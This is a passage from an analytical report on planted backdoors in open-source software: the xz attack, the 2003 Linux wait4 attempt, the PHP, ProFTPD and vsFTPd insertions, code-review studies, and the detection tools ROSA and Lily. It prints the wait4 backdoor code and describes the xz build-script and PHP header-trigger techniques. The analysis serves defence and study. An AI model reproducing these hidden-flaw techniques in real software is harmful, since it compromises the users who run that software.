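According to LWN's technical article on the backdoor, projects that use the build tool Autoconf publish tarballs containing generated build files that the repository lacks. An extra file in the xz tarball was therefore not suspicious in itself. The script was a modified copy of a real one from Gnulib, a shared collection of code. Jia Tan had updated the copyright year and added some obscure lines, one of which searched the source for a pattern of characters that appeared only in the "corrupt" test file. Cox calls the result "a fairly plausible set of diffs, in case anyone thought to check".

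Jia Tan had also raised the script's version number from 3 to 30. The standard tool for refreshing such scripts apparently keeps the copy with the higher number, so a distribution that regenerated its build files would not have replaced the malicious copy.

Two parties could have checked the tarball. The first was Collin, who had noticed wrong file permissions and owners in the earlier 5.4.5 tarball. Jia Tan had probably typed the wrong command to create it. When Collin asked about it, Jia Tan wouldn't admit the mistake, although that would have been the easiest way to end the questions. Collin compared the tarball with one he had built himself, and everything else matched, so he let the release go ahead. In his notes, he mentions no such comparison for 5.6.0 or 5.6.1 before their release.

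The second group was the packagers, who prepare software for each distribution. They built from the downloaded tarballs, and none reported the altered script.

In the last step, the script changed the build instructions on the machine compiling xz, and scattered its additions so that nobody would see them together. It did this only on 64-bit Intel-type Linux systems, with particular compilers, and when building a Debian package or an RPM package, the format that Fedora and Red Hat use. A suspicious programmer who compiled the same tarball at home would normally have got a clean library.

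### Half a second

Freund found the backdoor by accident. On machines running Debian's development version, he noticed that ssh logins were using a lot of processor time and that Valgrind, a tool that detects improper use of memory, reported errors in liblzma. He timed a login that was bound to fail, and it took 0.8 seconds with the new version of the library and 0.3 with the old one. The delay came from the backdoor's slow search through tables of function names in memory while sshd started.

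Freund then compared what the processor did with the backdoor active and inactive. This was difficult because the backdoor stayed inactive if it detected certain debugging tools or signs that someone had started sshd by hand. Freund, who says he is not a security researcher, first assumed that someone had tampered with Debian's package. He found that the tarballs and the repository were the source only after tracing the fault.

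Valgrind, an automatic tool, had nearly exposed the attack earlier. Valgrind errors caused by the backdoor began to appear in Red Hat's distributions on 4 March. Jia Tan, who was expected to deal with them, was able to explain them away and committed a supposed fix on 8 March as a distraction. The real fix came the next day in the replacement test files.

Version 5.6.0 had been public for 34 days when Freund posted his warning. It had reached Debian's unstable and testing versions, Fedora's development version and the Fedora 40 beta, and openSUSE Tumbleweed, which updates continuously. Freund wrote that most distributions that had adopted the releases had them only in pre-release versions. Arch, Gentoo and NixOS didn't link sshd to liblzma, so the backdoor couldn't work there. Jia Tan was still seeking wider adoption on 28 March, when they asked Ubuntu to take 5.6.1. Przymus and Durieux know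 of no case in which anyone used the backdoor.

LWN describes two opposite reactions. Some people saw proof that open-source developers detect attacks, and others saw a disaster avoided by luck. According to LWN, both can be right, because Freund was lucky to notice the delay but could trace it only because the software was open to him. The discovery is weak evidence about code review, however, because Freund read the source only after timing measurements and a memory checker had led him to it. If the search had taken a hundredth of a second and the memory errors hadn't occurred, he would have had no reason to read it.

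### What kind of failure it was

One could treat xz as a case where expert reviewers missed a hidden flaw. The repository was public, the test files and the full stop were in it for weeks, and Collin knew the code better than anyone. Packagers at several distributions also accepted the tarballs.

Only the full stop fits that description well. It was a readable planted flaw, and someone other than its author probably handled it before it entered the code. The test files were visible but unreadable, and the build script never went through code review. The xz case therefore adds only one probable miss to the catch rate, for a flaw that had almost no effect.

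Collin was not a careless reviewer. In his notes on Jia Tan's ordinary changes, he records reverting one within days, fixing a memory leak in another and correcting an off-by-one error in a complicated rewrite of the decompression code. He also missed things. A fix from January 2023 broke something else, and he didn't notice until November. Judging by the experiments, this is roughly what one would expect from a skilled reviewer. Jia Tan had watched him work for two years and kept the decisive code out of the place where he reviewed changes.

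The other explanation, which accounts for more of what happened, is that the attacker took over the reviewer's job. By 2024 Jia Tan could approve changes, build and sign releases, receive bug reports and answer questions from distributions. Much of xz therefore no longer had a reviewer who was independent of the author, and a second reader protects a project only if they are independent of the first.

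Przymus and Durieux write that Jia Tan does not appear to have exploited the right to change the repository. This is hard to reconcile with the eight malicious commits they also count. But they are right that the release was the decisive step. Collin (writing as Larhzu, 2024) confirms in *xz backdoor* that the code that triggered the backdoor was never in the repository.

Within days, people disagreed about whether reviewers would have caught the script if it had been in the repository. mdeslaur (2024), commenting under LWN's *A backdoor in xz*, doubted that anyone would have noticed it there, and argued that it was easy to spot because the tarball and the repository didn't match. Another reader, epa, replied that the attacker had a choice and presumably picked the tarball as the safer place. On a Debian mailing list, in *Validating tarballs against git repositories* (2024), Vincent Bernat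 argued that if Debian had built from the repository, the attacker would have put the script there. Another participant replied that more developers now build and test from the repository, so one of them might have run into trouble sooner.

The attacker's choice is some evidence for epa's view, since Jia Tan knew who was reading the repository and how closely. But it shows only what Jia Tan expected. The script was short, dull and written in a build language that few people know well, and reviewers missed the full stop in a file that more people could read.

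Reviewers also skipped two checks, either of which would have exposed the backdoor without unusual skill. Nobody asked how the test files had been made, and no packager compared the new script with the original in Gnulib. Both checks would have seemed a waste of time for a project with no history of trouble, and a packager may be responsible for many such projects.

Collin's later review shows how much work a full check takes. He published a first version of his notes in mid-April and the finished version on 29 May, two months after the disclosure. He found almost all of Jia Tan's work sound, including all the earlier tarballs.

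He also concluded that some changes others had found suspicious were harmless. LWN wrote that Jia Tan had altered the project's security policy to limit the disclosure of vulnerabilities. Collin had in fact asked for a simpler policy, although he wanted a shorter waiting period than the 90 days Jia Tan preferred. As at Minnesota, people had suspected harmless changes because they distrusted the author.

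### Thompson's compiler

Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, explained why reading a program's source code isn't enough to know what the program does. In his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, published in 1984, he described a backdoor in a compiler, the program that translates source code into a form a computer can run.

The attacker first adds code to the compiler that recognises the source of the Unix login program and adds a secret password while translating it. The login program's source stays clean, but anyone who reads the compiler's source will see this code. So the attacker adds a second piece of code, which recognises the compiler's own source and inserts both pieces into the translation. The attacker compiles this version once, installs it and deletes both pieces from the source.

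From then on, none of the source code contains the backdoor. But programmers use the installed compiler to build the next one, so the backdoor passes to each new version. A reviewer could read every line of the login program and the compiler, correctly find nothing wrong, and still use a machine that accepts the secret password.

The xz attack was much simpler than Thompson's. Its build script was text, and anyone who unpacked the tarball could have read it. But Thompson's argument still applies, because users don't directly run the source code that reviewers approve. That code first goes through tarballs, build scripts, compilers and packaging tools, and an attacker who controls any of these can insert a backdoor without changing the reviewed source.

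Compression software is a useful target for an attacker who wants to compromise other programs. Many projects publish their source as .xz archives, so distributions use xz to unpack that source before compiling it. A malicious version of xz could in principle alter the source while unpacking it. The 2024 backdoor targeted sshd instead, but Debian still stopped its builds on 30 March to rebuild the machines that ran them.

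One answer to Thompson is to build a compiler without relying on an existing one. *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor* (Malka, 2025) describes how some distributions start from a tiny program, use it to build a simple assembler, and work up in stages to a modern compiler. Developers of the Guix distribution have reduced the starting program to 357 bytes, which is small enough for a person to check by hand.

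A similar procedure led NixOS to use the malicious tarball. NixOS needs xz at an early stage to unpack other software, and at that point it can't generate xz's build files because the tool that generates them, Autoconf, depends on xz. The tarball contained those files ready-made. NixOS therefore distributed the backdoored version to its users, though the backdoor couldn't work on their machines.

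### Remedies, and what each would have caught

Most of the technical remedies since 2024 try to close the gap between the reviewed source and the shipped program. They differ in which part of the gap they cover:

| Remedy | Script in the tarball | Code in the test files | Full stop |
|---|---|---|---|
| Build from the repository | Excluded from the build | Still there, but inactive | Not caught |
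| Compare the tarball with the repository | Visible among many harmless differences | Not caught | Not caught |
| Make the tarball reproducible | Caught | Not caught | Not caught |
| Make the build reproducible | Not caught | Not caught | Not caught |
| Build from both sources and compare the programs | Caught if the script runs during the test | Caught if the script activates it | Not caught |
| Check test programs for syntax errors | Not caught | Not caught | Caught |

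Arch Linux switched to building xz from the repository on 28 March 2024. Malka recommends this wherever possible, using archives that a hosting service such as GitHub generates automatically. An attacker would then have to compromise the hosting service or put the script where reviewers can see it. This approach still depends on reviewers noticing the script, and a commenter in *Should any conclusions be drawn from the xz backdoor?*, a discussion among Python developers, warns that a backdoor could go undetected in a repository for years.

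Comparing the tarball directly with the repository is not enough to identify tampering, because honest tarballs also contain many extra files. Daniel Stenberg, who maintains the widely used program curl, considers this difference a feature because it saves users from generating those files themselves. Simon Josefsson, in *Verified Reproducible Tarballs*, says poor auditing of such differences helped the xz attack, but he calls the auditing hard and boring work for humans and would rather they spent the time on the source itself.

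A reproducible tarball removes most of that work. Anyone can run the project's own procedure on the repository and check that the result is identical to the published file. PostgreSQL, the database Freund works on, has adopted this. If xz had done so, Jia Tan's modified script would have produced a mismatch. But the project's maintainers have to set up the procedure, so Malka expects adoption to be slow, and a malicious maintainer could make excuses to delay it.

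Reproducible builds are the best-known remedy, but on their own they would not have revealed the backdoor. A build is reproducible if repeating it under the same conditions produces a bit-for-bit identical program. Comparing builds from different machines can therefore expose tampering that happened on one of them during or after compilation. But xz was already reproducible, according to Malka. Two people who built a Debian package from the poisoned tarball would have got the same backdoored program and been falsely reassured by the match.

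Malka proposes building xz once from the tarball and once from the repository, then comparing the two programs. Harmless extra files should not change the result, so this avoids most of the irrelevant differences that appear when comparing the sources directly. However, Jia Tan's script activated the backdoor only during the build of a Debian or RPM package. In an ordinary NixOS build, both versions would presumably have lacked the backdoor, and the comparison would have found nothing. To catch an attack this selective, the targeted distribution has to run the test in its real build environment.

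As the table shows, these measures do little about the test files. A commenter under LWN's article suggested that the process that builds a program should have no access to its test data, which would have stopped the script from extracting the code, wherever the script came from. On the full stop, Przymus and Durieux report that Autoconf's developers were adding syntax checks for test programs and that CMake's were considering something similar.

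Other responses reduce the number of programs that an attacker can reach through one library. On 29 February 2024, a month before the disclosure, a developer proposed removing liblzma from systemd's library, and systemd accepted the change on 5 March. The change would have defeated the attack on sshd once distributions adopted it. Kevin Beaumont, a security researcher, has speculated that this prospect hurried the attacker.

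By autumn 2025 Debian had only partly adopted these measures. In *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected* (2025), the Debian developer Otto Kekäläinen audited Debian's xz package and reported that about 93% of Debian's source packages had a repository on its central server. Some important ones, including Bash and Coreutils, had none, and Debian's rules didn't require one. Nothing ensured that a package's repository matched what its maintainer had uploaded, although a newer system that uploads directly from the repository was becoming more popular.

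The tarballs still differed from their projects' repositories. The xz 5.8.1 tarball, released in 2025, contained many ready-made build files. Kekäläinen showed how to display the differences with standard tools, but someone has to choose to run those tools and read the output.

A packager could have found the altered build script by comparing it with the Gnulib original, so Open Source Security (2025), a podcast that interviewed Kekäläinen that November, went too far in calling xz a nearly impossible attack to detect. That description is closer to the truth for someone who read only the repository, where the full stop was the only sabotage in plain text.

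Collin released a clean version of xz in May 2024 and removed ifunc from the library. A longtime contributor to the Gentoo distribution, who had also worked on xz for years, became the second maintainer, which gives the project an independent reviewer again. The project chose this maintainer in much the same way as the last one, for a record of good work, but the new maintainer's record is longer, and much of it comes from another project where other people could judge it.

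## Other insertions that came to light, and flaws that lasted for years

The attacker behind the xz backdoor spent more than two years earning a maintainer's trust, but in four other known cases the attackers inserted their code without submitting it for review. Kokkonis and colleagues list three of these as confirmed attacks: those on the file-server programs ProFTPD and vsFTPd, and on the programming language PHP. The fourth is the 2003 attempt on the Linux kernel.

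| Target | How the code got in | Was a reviewer in the way? | How long it lasted | What revealed it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Linux kernel, 2003 | Someone edited a secondary copy of the source on a server | No | About a day | A nightly comparison with the master copy |
| ProFTPD, 2010 | An intruder replaced the release tarball on the download server | No | About three days | An outsider noticed the altered source |
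| vsFTPd, 2011 | An intruder replaced the release tarball on the download server | No | Two or three days | Someone warned the author, and the tarball failed its signature check |
| PHP, 2021 | Someone added commits under two developers' names | Only after the commit | A couple of hours | A developer reading new commits |

### One character in the Linux kernel

In 2003 the kernel developers kept their master copy in a system called BitKeeper. Some programmers refused to use it, so a server also offered an automatic copy in an older system, CVS. On 4 November someone added these two lines to the CVS copy, in a function called `wait4`:

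```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

Here `current->uid` is the identity of the user running the program, and 0 stands for root, who may do anything. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) suggests that an expert reading casually would take the lines for harmless error checking. They would be harmless with two equals signs, but a single one sets `current->uid` to 0, so any program that called `wait4` with that odd pair of options became root. The assignment also yields zero, which C treats as false, so the second line never ran, and the call returned the same error as it would without the new lines.

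The change was discovered because it had not arrived through the proper channel. Larry McVoy's company made BitKeeper and produced the CVS copy. McVoy (2003) explained in *BK2CVS problem* that an automatic check compared the BitKeeper and CVS copies every night and flagged the file. The new entries in the file's log also lacked the usual pointer to an approved change. They carried the name of David Miller, a well-known kernel developer, who denied making them.

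No reviewer had seen the lines before McVoy posted them to the mailing list in answer to a question. His post became a small, unplanned test of readers. McVoy himself had not noticed the single equals sign. Ten minutes later a reader replied that the lines looked odd, and within half an hour two more had recognised a backdoor. These readers had about as much help as a reviewer can get, because they had only two lines to examine and knew that nobody had authorised them.

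Torvalds said that the lines could not have reached a kernel release, because he read patches to core files before accepting them and the people whose work he merged directly did not use CVS. McVoy was less sure. A programmer working from the CVS copy could have unknowingly included the backdoor in a patch, and catching it would then have depended on Torvalds's reading of that patch.

Another developer, Theodore Ts'o, described a similar danger in the same discussion. Someone could email Torvalds a patch that claimed to fix a bug but opened a security hole. They could also bury it among plausible changes and forge a trusted developer's address. Seventeen years later, the Minnesota researchers tested the first part of that plan, the false bug fix.

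### Replaced archives and borrowed names

The intruders who attacked ProFTPD and vsFTPd changed the archives that users downloaded. In ProFTPD, a secret command gave the sender root access. In vsFTPd, a user name containing a smiley face opened a backdoor. Many projects sign each archive with a private key, so users who check the signature can tell if someone without the key has altered the archive. Signature checks could not have stopped the xz backdoor, because the attacker made the releases.

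The PHP case is the only one of the four in which a person found the backdoor by reading code. On 28 March 2021 someone added a commit in the name of Rasmus Lerdorf, PHP's creator, and labelled it a typo fix. According to DevStyler, the maintainer Nikita Popov said developers found it "a couple of hours" later, during a routine review of new commits, and removed it at once. A second malicious commit, in Popov's name, claimed to revert the fix.

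The developers deserve some credit for reading a commit presented as a typo fix from the project's founder, but the malicious code was barely hidden. If a visitor to a website sent a header beginning with "zerodium", the name of a company that trades in software vulnerabilities, the site would run whatever code followed. SecurityWeek reported that the commit also contained the text "REMOVETHIS: sold to zerodium, mid 2017". Popov called the changes "rather obviously malicious". Catching such code is weak evidence that a reviewer would catch the flaw in Åkesson's warhead detector.

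How the attacker got access is less certain. The developers first suspected that someone had broken into PHP's server, but Popov (2021) withdrew that explanation in an update on 6 April. He wrote that the server had also accepted changes from anyone with a valid password, which he had not known when he first responded, and that the password database may have leaked.

### What a list of discovered attacks leaves out

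None of the four insertions went to a reviewer before acceptance, so none should count toward a catch rate. Freedom to Tinker infers that the 2003 attacker avoided the approval process because reviewers might have noticed the change. However, the attacker may simply have found it easier to break into a weakly protected server than to write a patch that kernel developers wanted. Torvalds thought it "telling" that the attacker had gone for the CVS copy, but he was commenting on the security of the servers.

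The way people find insertions also biases the list. An intruder who alters one copy of a program makes it differ from the other copies, and an automatic comparison or a signature check can expose the difference without anyone understanding the code. A flaw that a reviewer has accepted creates no mismatch, because the master copy, the secondary copies and the signed release all contain it. The public record would therefore consist mainly of break-ins even if most successful attackers had gotten their flaws in through review.

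The same bias helps explain why these insertions lasted only hours or days. Three of them left a mismatch, and the fourth was blatant. We can infer little from these cases about how long a well-disguised flaw would last after a reviewer approved it.

### Reviewed changes that later needed a fix

Honest mistakes are much more common than known attacks, so researchers can count them in large numbers. *Investigating Code Review Quality*, by Kononenko, Baysal and colleagues, studied changes made during 2013 to Mozilla's main repository, which holds the Firefox browser's source code. At least one reviewer had to approve each patch. The researchers matched 27,270 commits to 28,127 approving reviews and concluded that 54% of those reviews had missed a bug.

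They identified the bugs by working backwards from later fixes, with a method called SZZ:

1. Take a commit that fixes a reported bug, and list the lines it removed or replaced.
2. For each of those lines, find the earlier commit that last changed it.
3. Blame that commit for the bug, unless it was made after someone reported the bug.

The result depends heavily on what counts as a bug. Mozilla's tracking system numbers bug reports, feature requests and documentation changes in the same way, and the researchers treated them all as bugs. Four fifths of the commits they collected carried such a number, and most of the rest were merges or withdrawn changes. A reviewer who approved good code could therefore be counted as having missed a bug because someone later rewrote a line of it to add a feature.

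SZZ also tends to flag several earlier commits as possible sources of a bug. For 100 commits that the researchers checked by hand, it flagged 429 possible sources, or more than four each, before the check on dates. It flagged 39 of these (9%) wrongly because of changes to comments, formatting or blank lines. Most of the others had changed real code, but that doesn't mean they caused the bug.

Other errors have the opposite effect and leave bugs out. The method ignores lines that a fix only adds, so it doesn't attribute a missing check to anyone. For this reason, it could miss the unchecked number that most reviewers overlooked in the 2021 experiment by Braz and colleagues. The researchers also followed the code for only six months after the end of 2013, so they left out bugs that took longer to surface.

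In *Four Eyes Are Better Than Two*, Bavota and Russo applied a stricter version of the method to three other projects. They counted only reports that the project had classified as bugs and closed as fixed, and they ignored comments and blank lines. By this definition, 3% to 5% of reviewed commits led to a later fix, less than a tenth of the Mozilla figure. The projects also differ in other ways, but a measure that can change this much with its definition is a poor guide to how often reviewers miss bugs.

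Their study has one advantage over Mozilla's, which is that many commits in these projects never had a review:

| Project | Reviewed commits that led to a fix | Unreviewed commits that led to a fix |
|---|---|---|
| Android programming interfaces | 81 of 1,602 (5%) | 8,322 of 31,761 (26%) |
| LibreOffice | 147 of 5,337 (3%) | 2,547 of 45,763 (6%) |
| Scilab | 129 of 2,499 (5%) | 15 of 134 (11%) |

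(The paper's text gives 17% for unreviewed Android commits and 13% for Scilab, which don't match the counts in its table.)

If reviewed and unreviewed commits had been equally faulty to begin with, the difference would show what share of faulty commits review had stopped or repaired:

share stopped = 1 − (faulty share of reviewed ÷ faulty share of unreviewed)

This gives 51% for LibreOffice, 54% for Scilab and 81% for Android. The first two are close to the 56.6% baseline that Wu and Lu calculated for kernel patches, but the assumption behind these estimates is doubtful because commits weren't assigned to review at random. Developers may have skipped review for urgent changes or for work by trusted colleagues. Unreviewed Android commits were also larger on average, and SZZ blames larger commits more often. In the other two projects, however, reviewed commits were larger and still led to fewer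 fixes, so review probably does stop many accidental bugs.

The Mozilla data are more useful for comparing reviews, since the same flawed measure applies to all of them. Patches were more likely to need a later change if they were larger, touched more files, or were approved by a reviewer with a long queue of other requests. Experienced reviewers did somewhat better. A hostile author can exploit most of this, because Mozilla's contributors choose the size of a patch and which reviewer to ask, so an attacker could pick a busy one. The advantage might be small, because the researchers' models explained only 12% to 17% of the variation.

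People sometimes judge reviewers by the share of their comments that concern defects or security. A 2015 paper by Microsoft researchers argued that reviews often fail to find bugs, partly on the grounds that only about 15% of comments point to a possible defect. Entropic Thoughts' *Code Reviews Do Find Bugs* criticises that argument. A reviewer who found every defect would still have a low percentage if they also left many remarks about style. The estimate that 1% of review comments concern security has the same limitation.

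### How long an honest flaw can last

Some accidental flaws survive for years after a reviewer has missed them. One of the kernel vulnerabilities that Wu and Lu describe lasted five years. Another serious flaw appeared in the Debian distribution in 2006, when a maintainer removed code from the encryption library OpenSSL because it triggered warnings in the debugging tool Valgrind. The code supplied most of the randomness for new keys. For about 20 months, Debian machines generated keys that an attacker could guess from a fairly short list.

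Honest flaws like these give a rough idea of how long a deniable planted flaw could last, since the code may look the same. Suppose that people find flaws of some kind at a steady rate and that the average flaw lasts *L* years. The share still undiscovered after *t* years is then

e^(−t/L)

If such flaws lasted five years on average, a figure used only for illustration, 82% would survive their first year and 37% would survive five. An attacker who wants access for a few months therefore wouldn't need to hide a flaw especially well.

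The average lifetime of known flaws is likely to be too low an estimate for all flaws, because it leaves out the ones that nobody has found yet. A planted flaw may last even longer if its author has tested it against the usual tools and put it where few people look. But attackers use their flaws, and a victim who investigates a break-in may trace it back to the code, which can't happen with an accidental flaw that nobody exploits.

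### "goto fail" and the problem of intent

In February 2014 Apple repaired a flaw in the code that its phones and computers used to check the identity of secure websites. In simplified form, the faulty part looked like this:

```c
if ((err = update_hash(...)) != 0)
    goto fail;
    goto fail;
if ((err = finish_hash(...)) != 0)
    goto fail;
```

The instruction `goto fail` jumps to the end of the function, which then reports whether an error has occurred. In C, an `if` without braces controls only the next instruction. The first `goto fail` therefore runs only if something has gone wrong, but the second, despite its indentation, runs even if nothing has. It skips the remaining steps, including the check of the website's signature, and the function reports success because no error has occurred so far. Someone who controlled the network could impersonate a secure website, and iPhones had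 been exposed for well over a year.

A programmer could easily have duplicated the line by accident, by pasting it twice or merging two versions of the file badly, but it would also have been a neat way for an attacker to disable the signature check. The flaw became public months after Edward Snowden's leaks about American surveillance, and some commentators suspected an intelligence agency. There is no public evidence that anyone planted it, and an accident is the simpler explanation, but the code alone doesn't rule out a deliberate insertion.

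The reasoning can be written as a rule for updating odds:

odds of intent after reading the code = odds before × P(code | attacker) ÷ P(code | honest author)

Suppose that one serious flaw in a thousand is deliberate, and that an attacker is five times as likely as an honest programmer to produce a particular flaw. The chance that this flaw was deliberate is still only about one in 200. A flaw is plausibly deniable when an honest programmer would be about as likely to produce it as an attacker. Wheeler observed that many underhanded programs achieve this by copying mistakes that developers already make.

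The 2003 kernel lines were easier to judge, and some of the evidence was in the code. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) points out that `wait4` had no reason to deal with user identities. A commenter under Freedom to Tinker's article added that the corrected version, with two equals signs, would have made no sense either, because it would have rejected a harmless pair of options only for root. Chad Kitching, one of the first readers to suspect a backdoor, noticed that the next line of the function overwrote the error code anyway.

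The extra parentheses around the assignment do not show that the flaw was deliberate. A reader on the mailing list drew attention to them, since they prevent a compiler warning, and others later took them as proof of intent. But as another commenter noted, C would have rejected the assignment without them, so a programmer who mistyped the comparison by accident would have needed them too.

How the change arrived was much stronger evidence. The CVS copy was supposed to change only automatically, so an honest programmer had no ordinary reason to edit it. If the same two lines had come in a patch from a known contributor, a reviewer who spotted the error might have corrected it and thought no more about it.

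Some deliberate flaws may therefore already be on record as mistakes, and nobody knows how many. Most serious flaws are accidents, so treating every one as a possible attack would not solve this, and suspicion can fall on the wrong people, as it did at Minnesota. The Debian flaw also led to speculation about an intelligence agency, but the researcher who examined that possibility for Freedom to Tinker concluded that the flaw was probably not a backdoor. To tell deliberate flaws from mistakes more reliably, investigators need evidence from outside the code, such as who made the change, how it arrived and what else that person submitted. Outsiders don't have that evidence for "goto fail", because Apple published the source code of its releases without the history of individual changes.

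## Automated detection, and code written by AI systems

Automatic checks that weren't designed to detect backdoors exposed the 2003 attempt to put one in the Linux kernel and nearly exposed the xz backdoor. The first check compared two copies of the kernel's source code, and the second reported misused memory. Fuzzing is less likely to find a backdoor by luck, because a fuzzer tries a huge number of inputs but mainly reports crashes. It could enter a backdoor's secret password by chance, gain access, and record nothing unusual.

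### ROSA and the wrong password that works

Kokkonis and colleagues built ROSA to make a fuzzer recognise when an input triggers a backdoor. The tool relies on the idea that similar inputs should have similar effects. In their backdoored copy of sudo, for example, every wrong password should produce an error message, but "let_me_in" takes nearly the same path through the program and then runs a command.

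To compare effects, ROSA records system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system, for example to open a file or start another program. It works in three steps:

1. Fuzz the program for one minute, and keep the inputs that take new paths through it as examples of normal behaviour.
2. Fuzz the program for several hours. For each new input, find the stored example that took the most similar path.
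3. If the two inputs cause different types of system call, report both to a human expert.

ROSA measures similarity by the Hamming distance, the number of places in which two lists differ. Suppose a program has four possible steps and a new input triggers all of them, written 1111. One stored example triggered the first and third steps (1010), and another triggered only the second (0100). Their distances from the new input are 2 and 3, so ROSA picks the first example. If the new input made the program open and read files, while that example only made it open them, ROSA reports the pair.

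The one-minute sample is a compromise. A shorter sample misses more kinds of normal input, which then cause false alarms. A longer one is more likely to include the backdoor's secret input, which ROSA would then treat as normal. The sample included the secret input in about 6% of runs, but this never prevented detection, because other inputs still revealed the backdoor.

The test set was the 17 backdoors mentioned earlier. Seven are authentic: four from internet routers and three from the attacks on PHP, ProFTPD and vsFTPd. A researcher who had not worked on ROSA planted the other ten in widely used programs. ROSA had ten eight-hour runs on each backdoor, plus ten extra runs on one of the routers. It found the backdoor in 156 of the 180 runs (87%), after an hour and a half on average.

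Kokkonis and colleagues say that ROSA found all 17 backdoors, but it found the one in a Belkin router only after the researchers supplied starting inputs aimed at the code that reads web addresses, a convenient place to hide a secret trigger. ROSA missed that backdoor in all ten runs with standard starting inputs and found it in seven of ten runs with the targeted ones. An auditor who doesn't know that a backdoor exists would have to guess where to aim the inputs.

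All 24 failed runs failed because the fuzzer never generated an input that triggered the backdoor. ROSA recognised such inputs whenever the fuzzer generated them. The researchers left xz out of the test set because its backdoor responds only to someone with the attacker's private key, so a fuzzer would have to break the cryptography to trigger it.

An expert still has to check the inputs that ROSA reports as suspicious. There were seven on average, and each took about two minutes to check. The worst case was the database program SQLite, with up to 31 inputs, or about an hour's work. The expert compares two lists of system calls and doesn't need to read the program's code. For ProFTPD, the system calls showed the file server trying to open a command line with root access, which no file server should do.

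An older tool, Stringer, searches programs for suspicious pieces of fixed text. It found only four of the 17 backdoors and gave the expert an average of 308 pieces of text to check. Every program in the comparison contained a backdoor, so the results don't show how well an expert would recognize that seven suspicious inputs from a clean program are all harmless.

### Lily and the ten-minute check

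Several hours of fuzzing may be acceptable in an audit of a finished program, but not for every commit. Projects that fuzz each commit often allow about ten minutes. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) describes a second tool, Lily, that works within this limit by comparing the program before and after a change.

Lily raises an alarm only when an input makes the new version of a program produce a combination of system calls that it doesn't produce on a collection of ordinary test inputs, and the old version doesn't produce that combination on the same input. The first condition excludes behavior the update adds to every request, such as writing to a log, because the ordinary inputs cause it too. The second excludes odd behavior on rare inputs that was already there before the update.

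On harmless commits, Lily raised a false alarm in 14% of runs with only the first condition, 10% with only the second, and 0.2% with both.

Lily then shows a person which changed lines ran when the suspicious input went through the program, and marks those that made the unusual system calls. The backdoored release of vsFTPd differed from the previous release by 1,407 lines in five files, and Lily's report narrowed this to seven lines in one file. Releases of PHP differed by about two million lines on average, and Lily's reports on them averaged 11 lines.

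The researchers tested Lily on 13 of the 17 backdoors, leaving out those in routers because the source code wasn't available. They planted each backdoor in a commit and in several releases, and ran Lily 20 times on every case. They also ran it on 432 harmless commits and 50 harmless releases.

| | ROSA | Lily on commits | Lily on releases |
|---|---|---|---|
| Backdoored cases | 17 programs | 13 commits | 50 releases |
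| Length of each run | 8 hours | 10 minutes | 10 minutes |
| Runs that found the backdoor | 156 of 180 (87%) | 233 of 260 (90%) | 828 of 1,000 (83%) |
| False alarms on harmless cases | Not measured | 17 of 8,640 runs (0.2%) | 43 of 1,000 runs (4.3%) |
| Work left for a person | About 7 inputs, 2 minutes each | Read a short report | Read 1 to 12 lines on average, depending on the program |
| Included xz | No | No | No |

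Two updates to the sound library libsndfile caused 40 of the 43 false alarms on releases. Most false alarms on commits came from very large merges in PHP.

Lily detected every backdoor at least once in 20 runs, but a project would normally check each commit only once, so the 90% figure is more useful. A miss also matters more than it would with ROSA, because once a backdoored commit is in the program, the next comparison treats the backdoor as old behaviour and ignores it. A distribution that compares whole releases could still detect the backdoor, although the same weakness in the fuzzing may cause both checks to miss it.

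Kokkonis and colleagues write that Lily could have prevented the attacks on PHP, ProFTPD and vsFTPd. Their claim is most convincing for vsFTPd, where Lily found the backdoor in every run. It found the PHP backdoor in 16 of 20 runs on the malicious commit. For ProFTPD, where the real attacker replaced a release, Lily succeeded in only 34 of 80 runs on releases.

The low false-alarm rate matters because backdoors are rare. If one commit in 10,000 contained a backdoor like those in the test, Lily would probably catch it and would also raise about 20 false alarms on the other 9,999. Only about one alarm in 20 would be real, but a maintainer could probably handle them, since each comes with a short list of lines to read.

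Another approach is to look for suspicious contributor behaviour in the project's history, without examining the code. According to Kokkonis and colleagues, a machine-learning tool of this kind detected 15 of 19 attacks (79%) but had a false-alarm rate of about 11%. If that rate applied to each commit, the same 10,000 commits would produce more than 1,000 false alarms. The two sets of attacks had only the PHP case in common, so the detection rates aren't directly comparable.

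### How an attacker could avoid both tools

The simplest way to avoid a fuzzer is to put the backdoor in code that the fuzzer doesn't run. Kokkonis and colleagues measured coverage for 337 commits that changed code and found that the fuzzer had run only about 32% of the changed code on average. The low coverage probably also makes Lily's false-alarm rate lower than it would otherwise be, because the tool can't raise an alarm about code it never runs. The researchers attribute the low coverage to the harnesses, the small programs that connect a fuzzer to a project's code, and report that modern harnesses usually bring coverage close to complete.

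An attacker can also put the backdoor behind a cryptographic check, as in xz. Kokkonis and colleagues argue that this could backfire, because developers who read coverage reports would notice new code that the fuzzer can't reach. They suggest that this may be why the xz attackers disabled fuzzing. But if fuzzers don't reach two thirds of the changed code in a typical commit, a little more unreached code will not stand out.

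Kokkonis and colleagues discuss the xz attack but did not test Lily on it. Lily would probably have missed the backdoor, because the fuzzer would have needed both the private key and a version of the library that contained the backdoor, which Jia Tan's script inserted only while building Debian or RPM packages. Jia Tan might also have been able to skip the check, since many projects let their core maintainers do this. Kokkonis and colleagues therefore recommend that the hosting platform run Lily, outside the project's control.

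In a more elaborate attack, the attacker adds the backdoor's secret input to the ordinary test collection so that Lily treats it as normal. When the researchers added 100 such inputs, detection fell from 90% to 54% for commits and from 83% to 46% for releases. A stricter mode removed the planted inputs and restored detection, but it raised the false alarm rate to about 2.5% for harmless commits and to 18% for harmless releases. The researchers suggest using this mode on a random selection of changes, so that an attacker can't know when it will run.

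A larger limitation is the kind of harm the two tools can detect. Most of the backdoors in the test set let someone run commands or bypass a login, and all of them change the program's system calls. Åkesson's warhead detector does not let anyone do either, and it would make the same system calls whether or not its answer was correct. The same is probably true of many programs that miscount votes.

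The test set contains no flaws of this deniable kind. The ROSA paper calls deliberately planted bugs "bugdoors" and says that established tools for finding accidental bugs can detect them. Wheeler's results with the vote counters give that claim some support, though nobody wrote those programs to defeat his countermeasures.

### Language models as reviewers

A language model can read a code change and comment on it as a human reviewer would. It doesn't depend on a fuzzer reaching the code, and it could in principle detect an error that never affects a system call.

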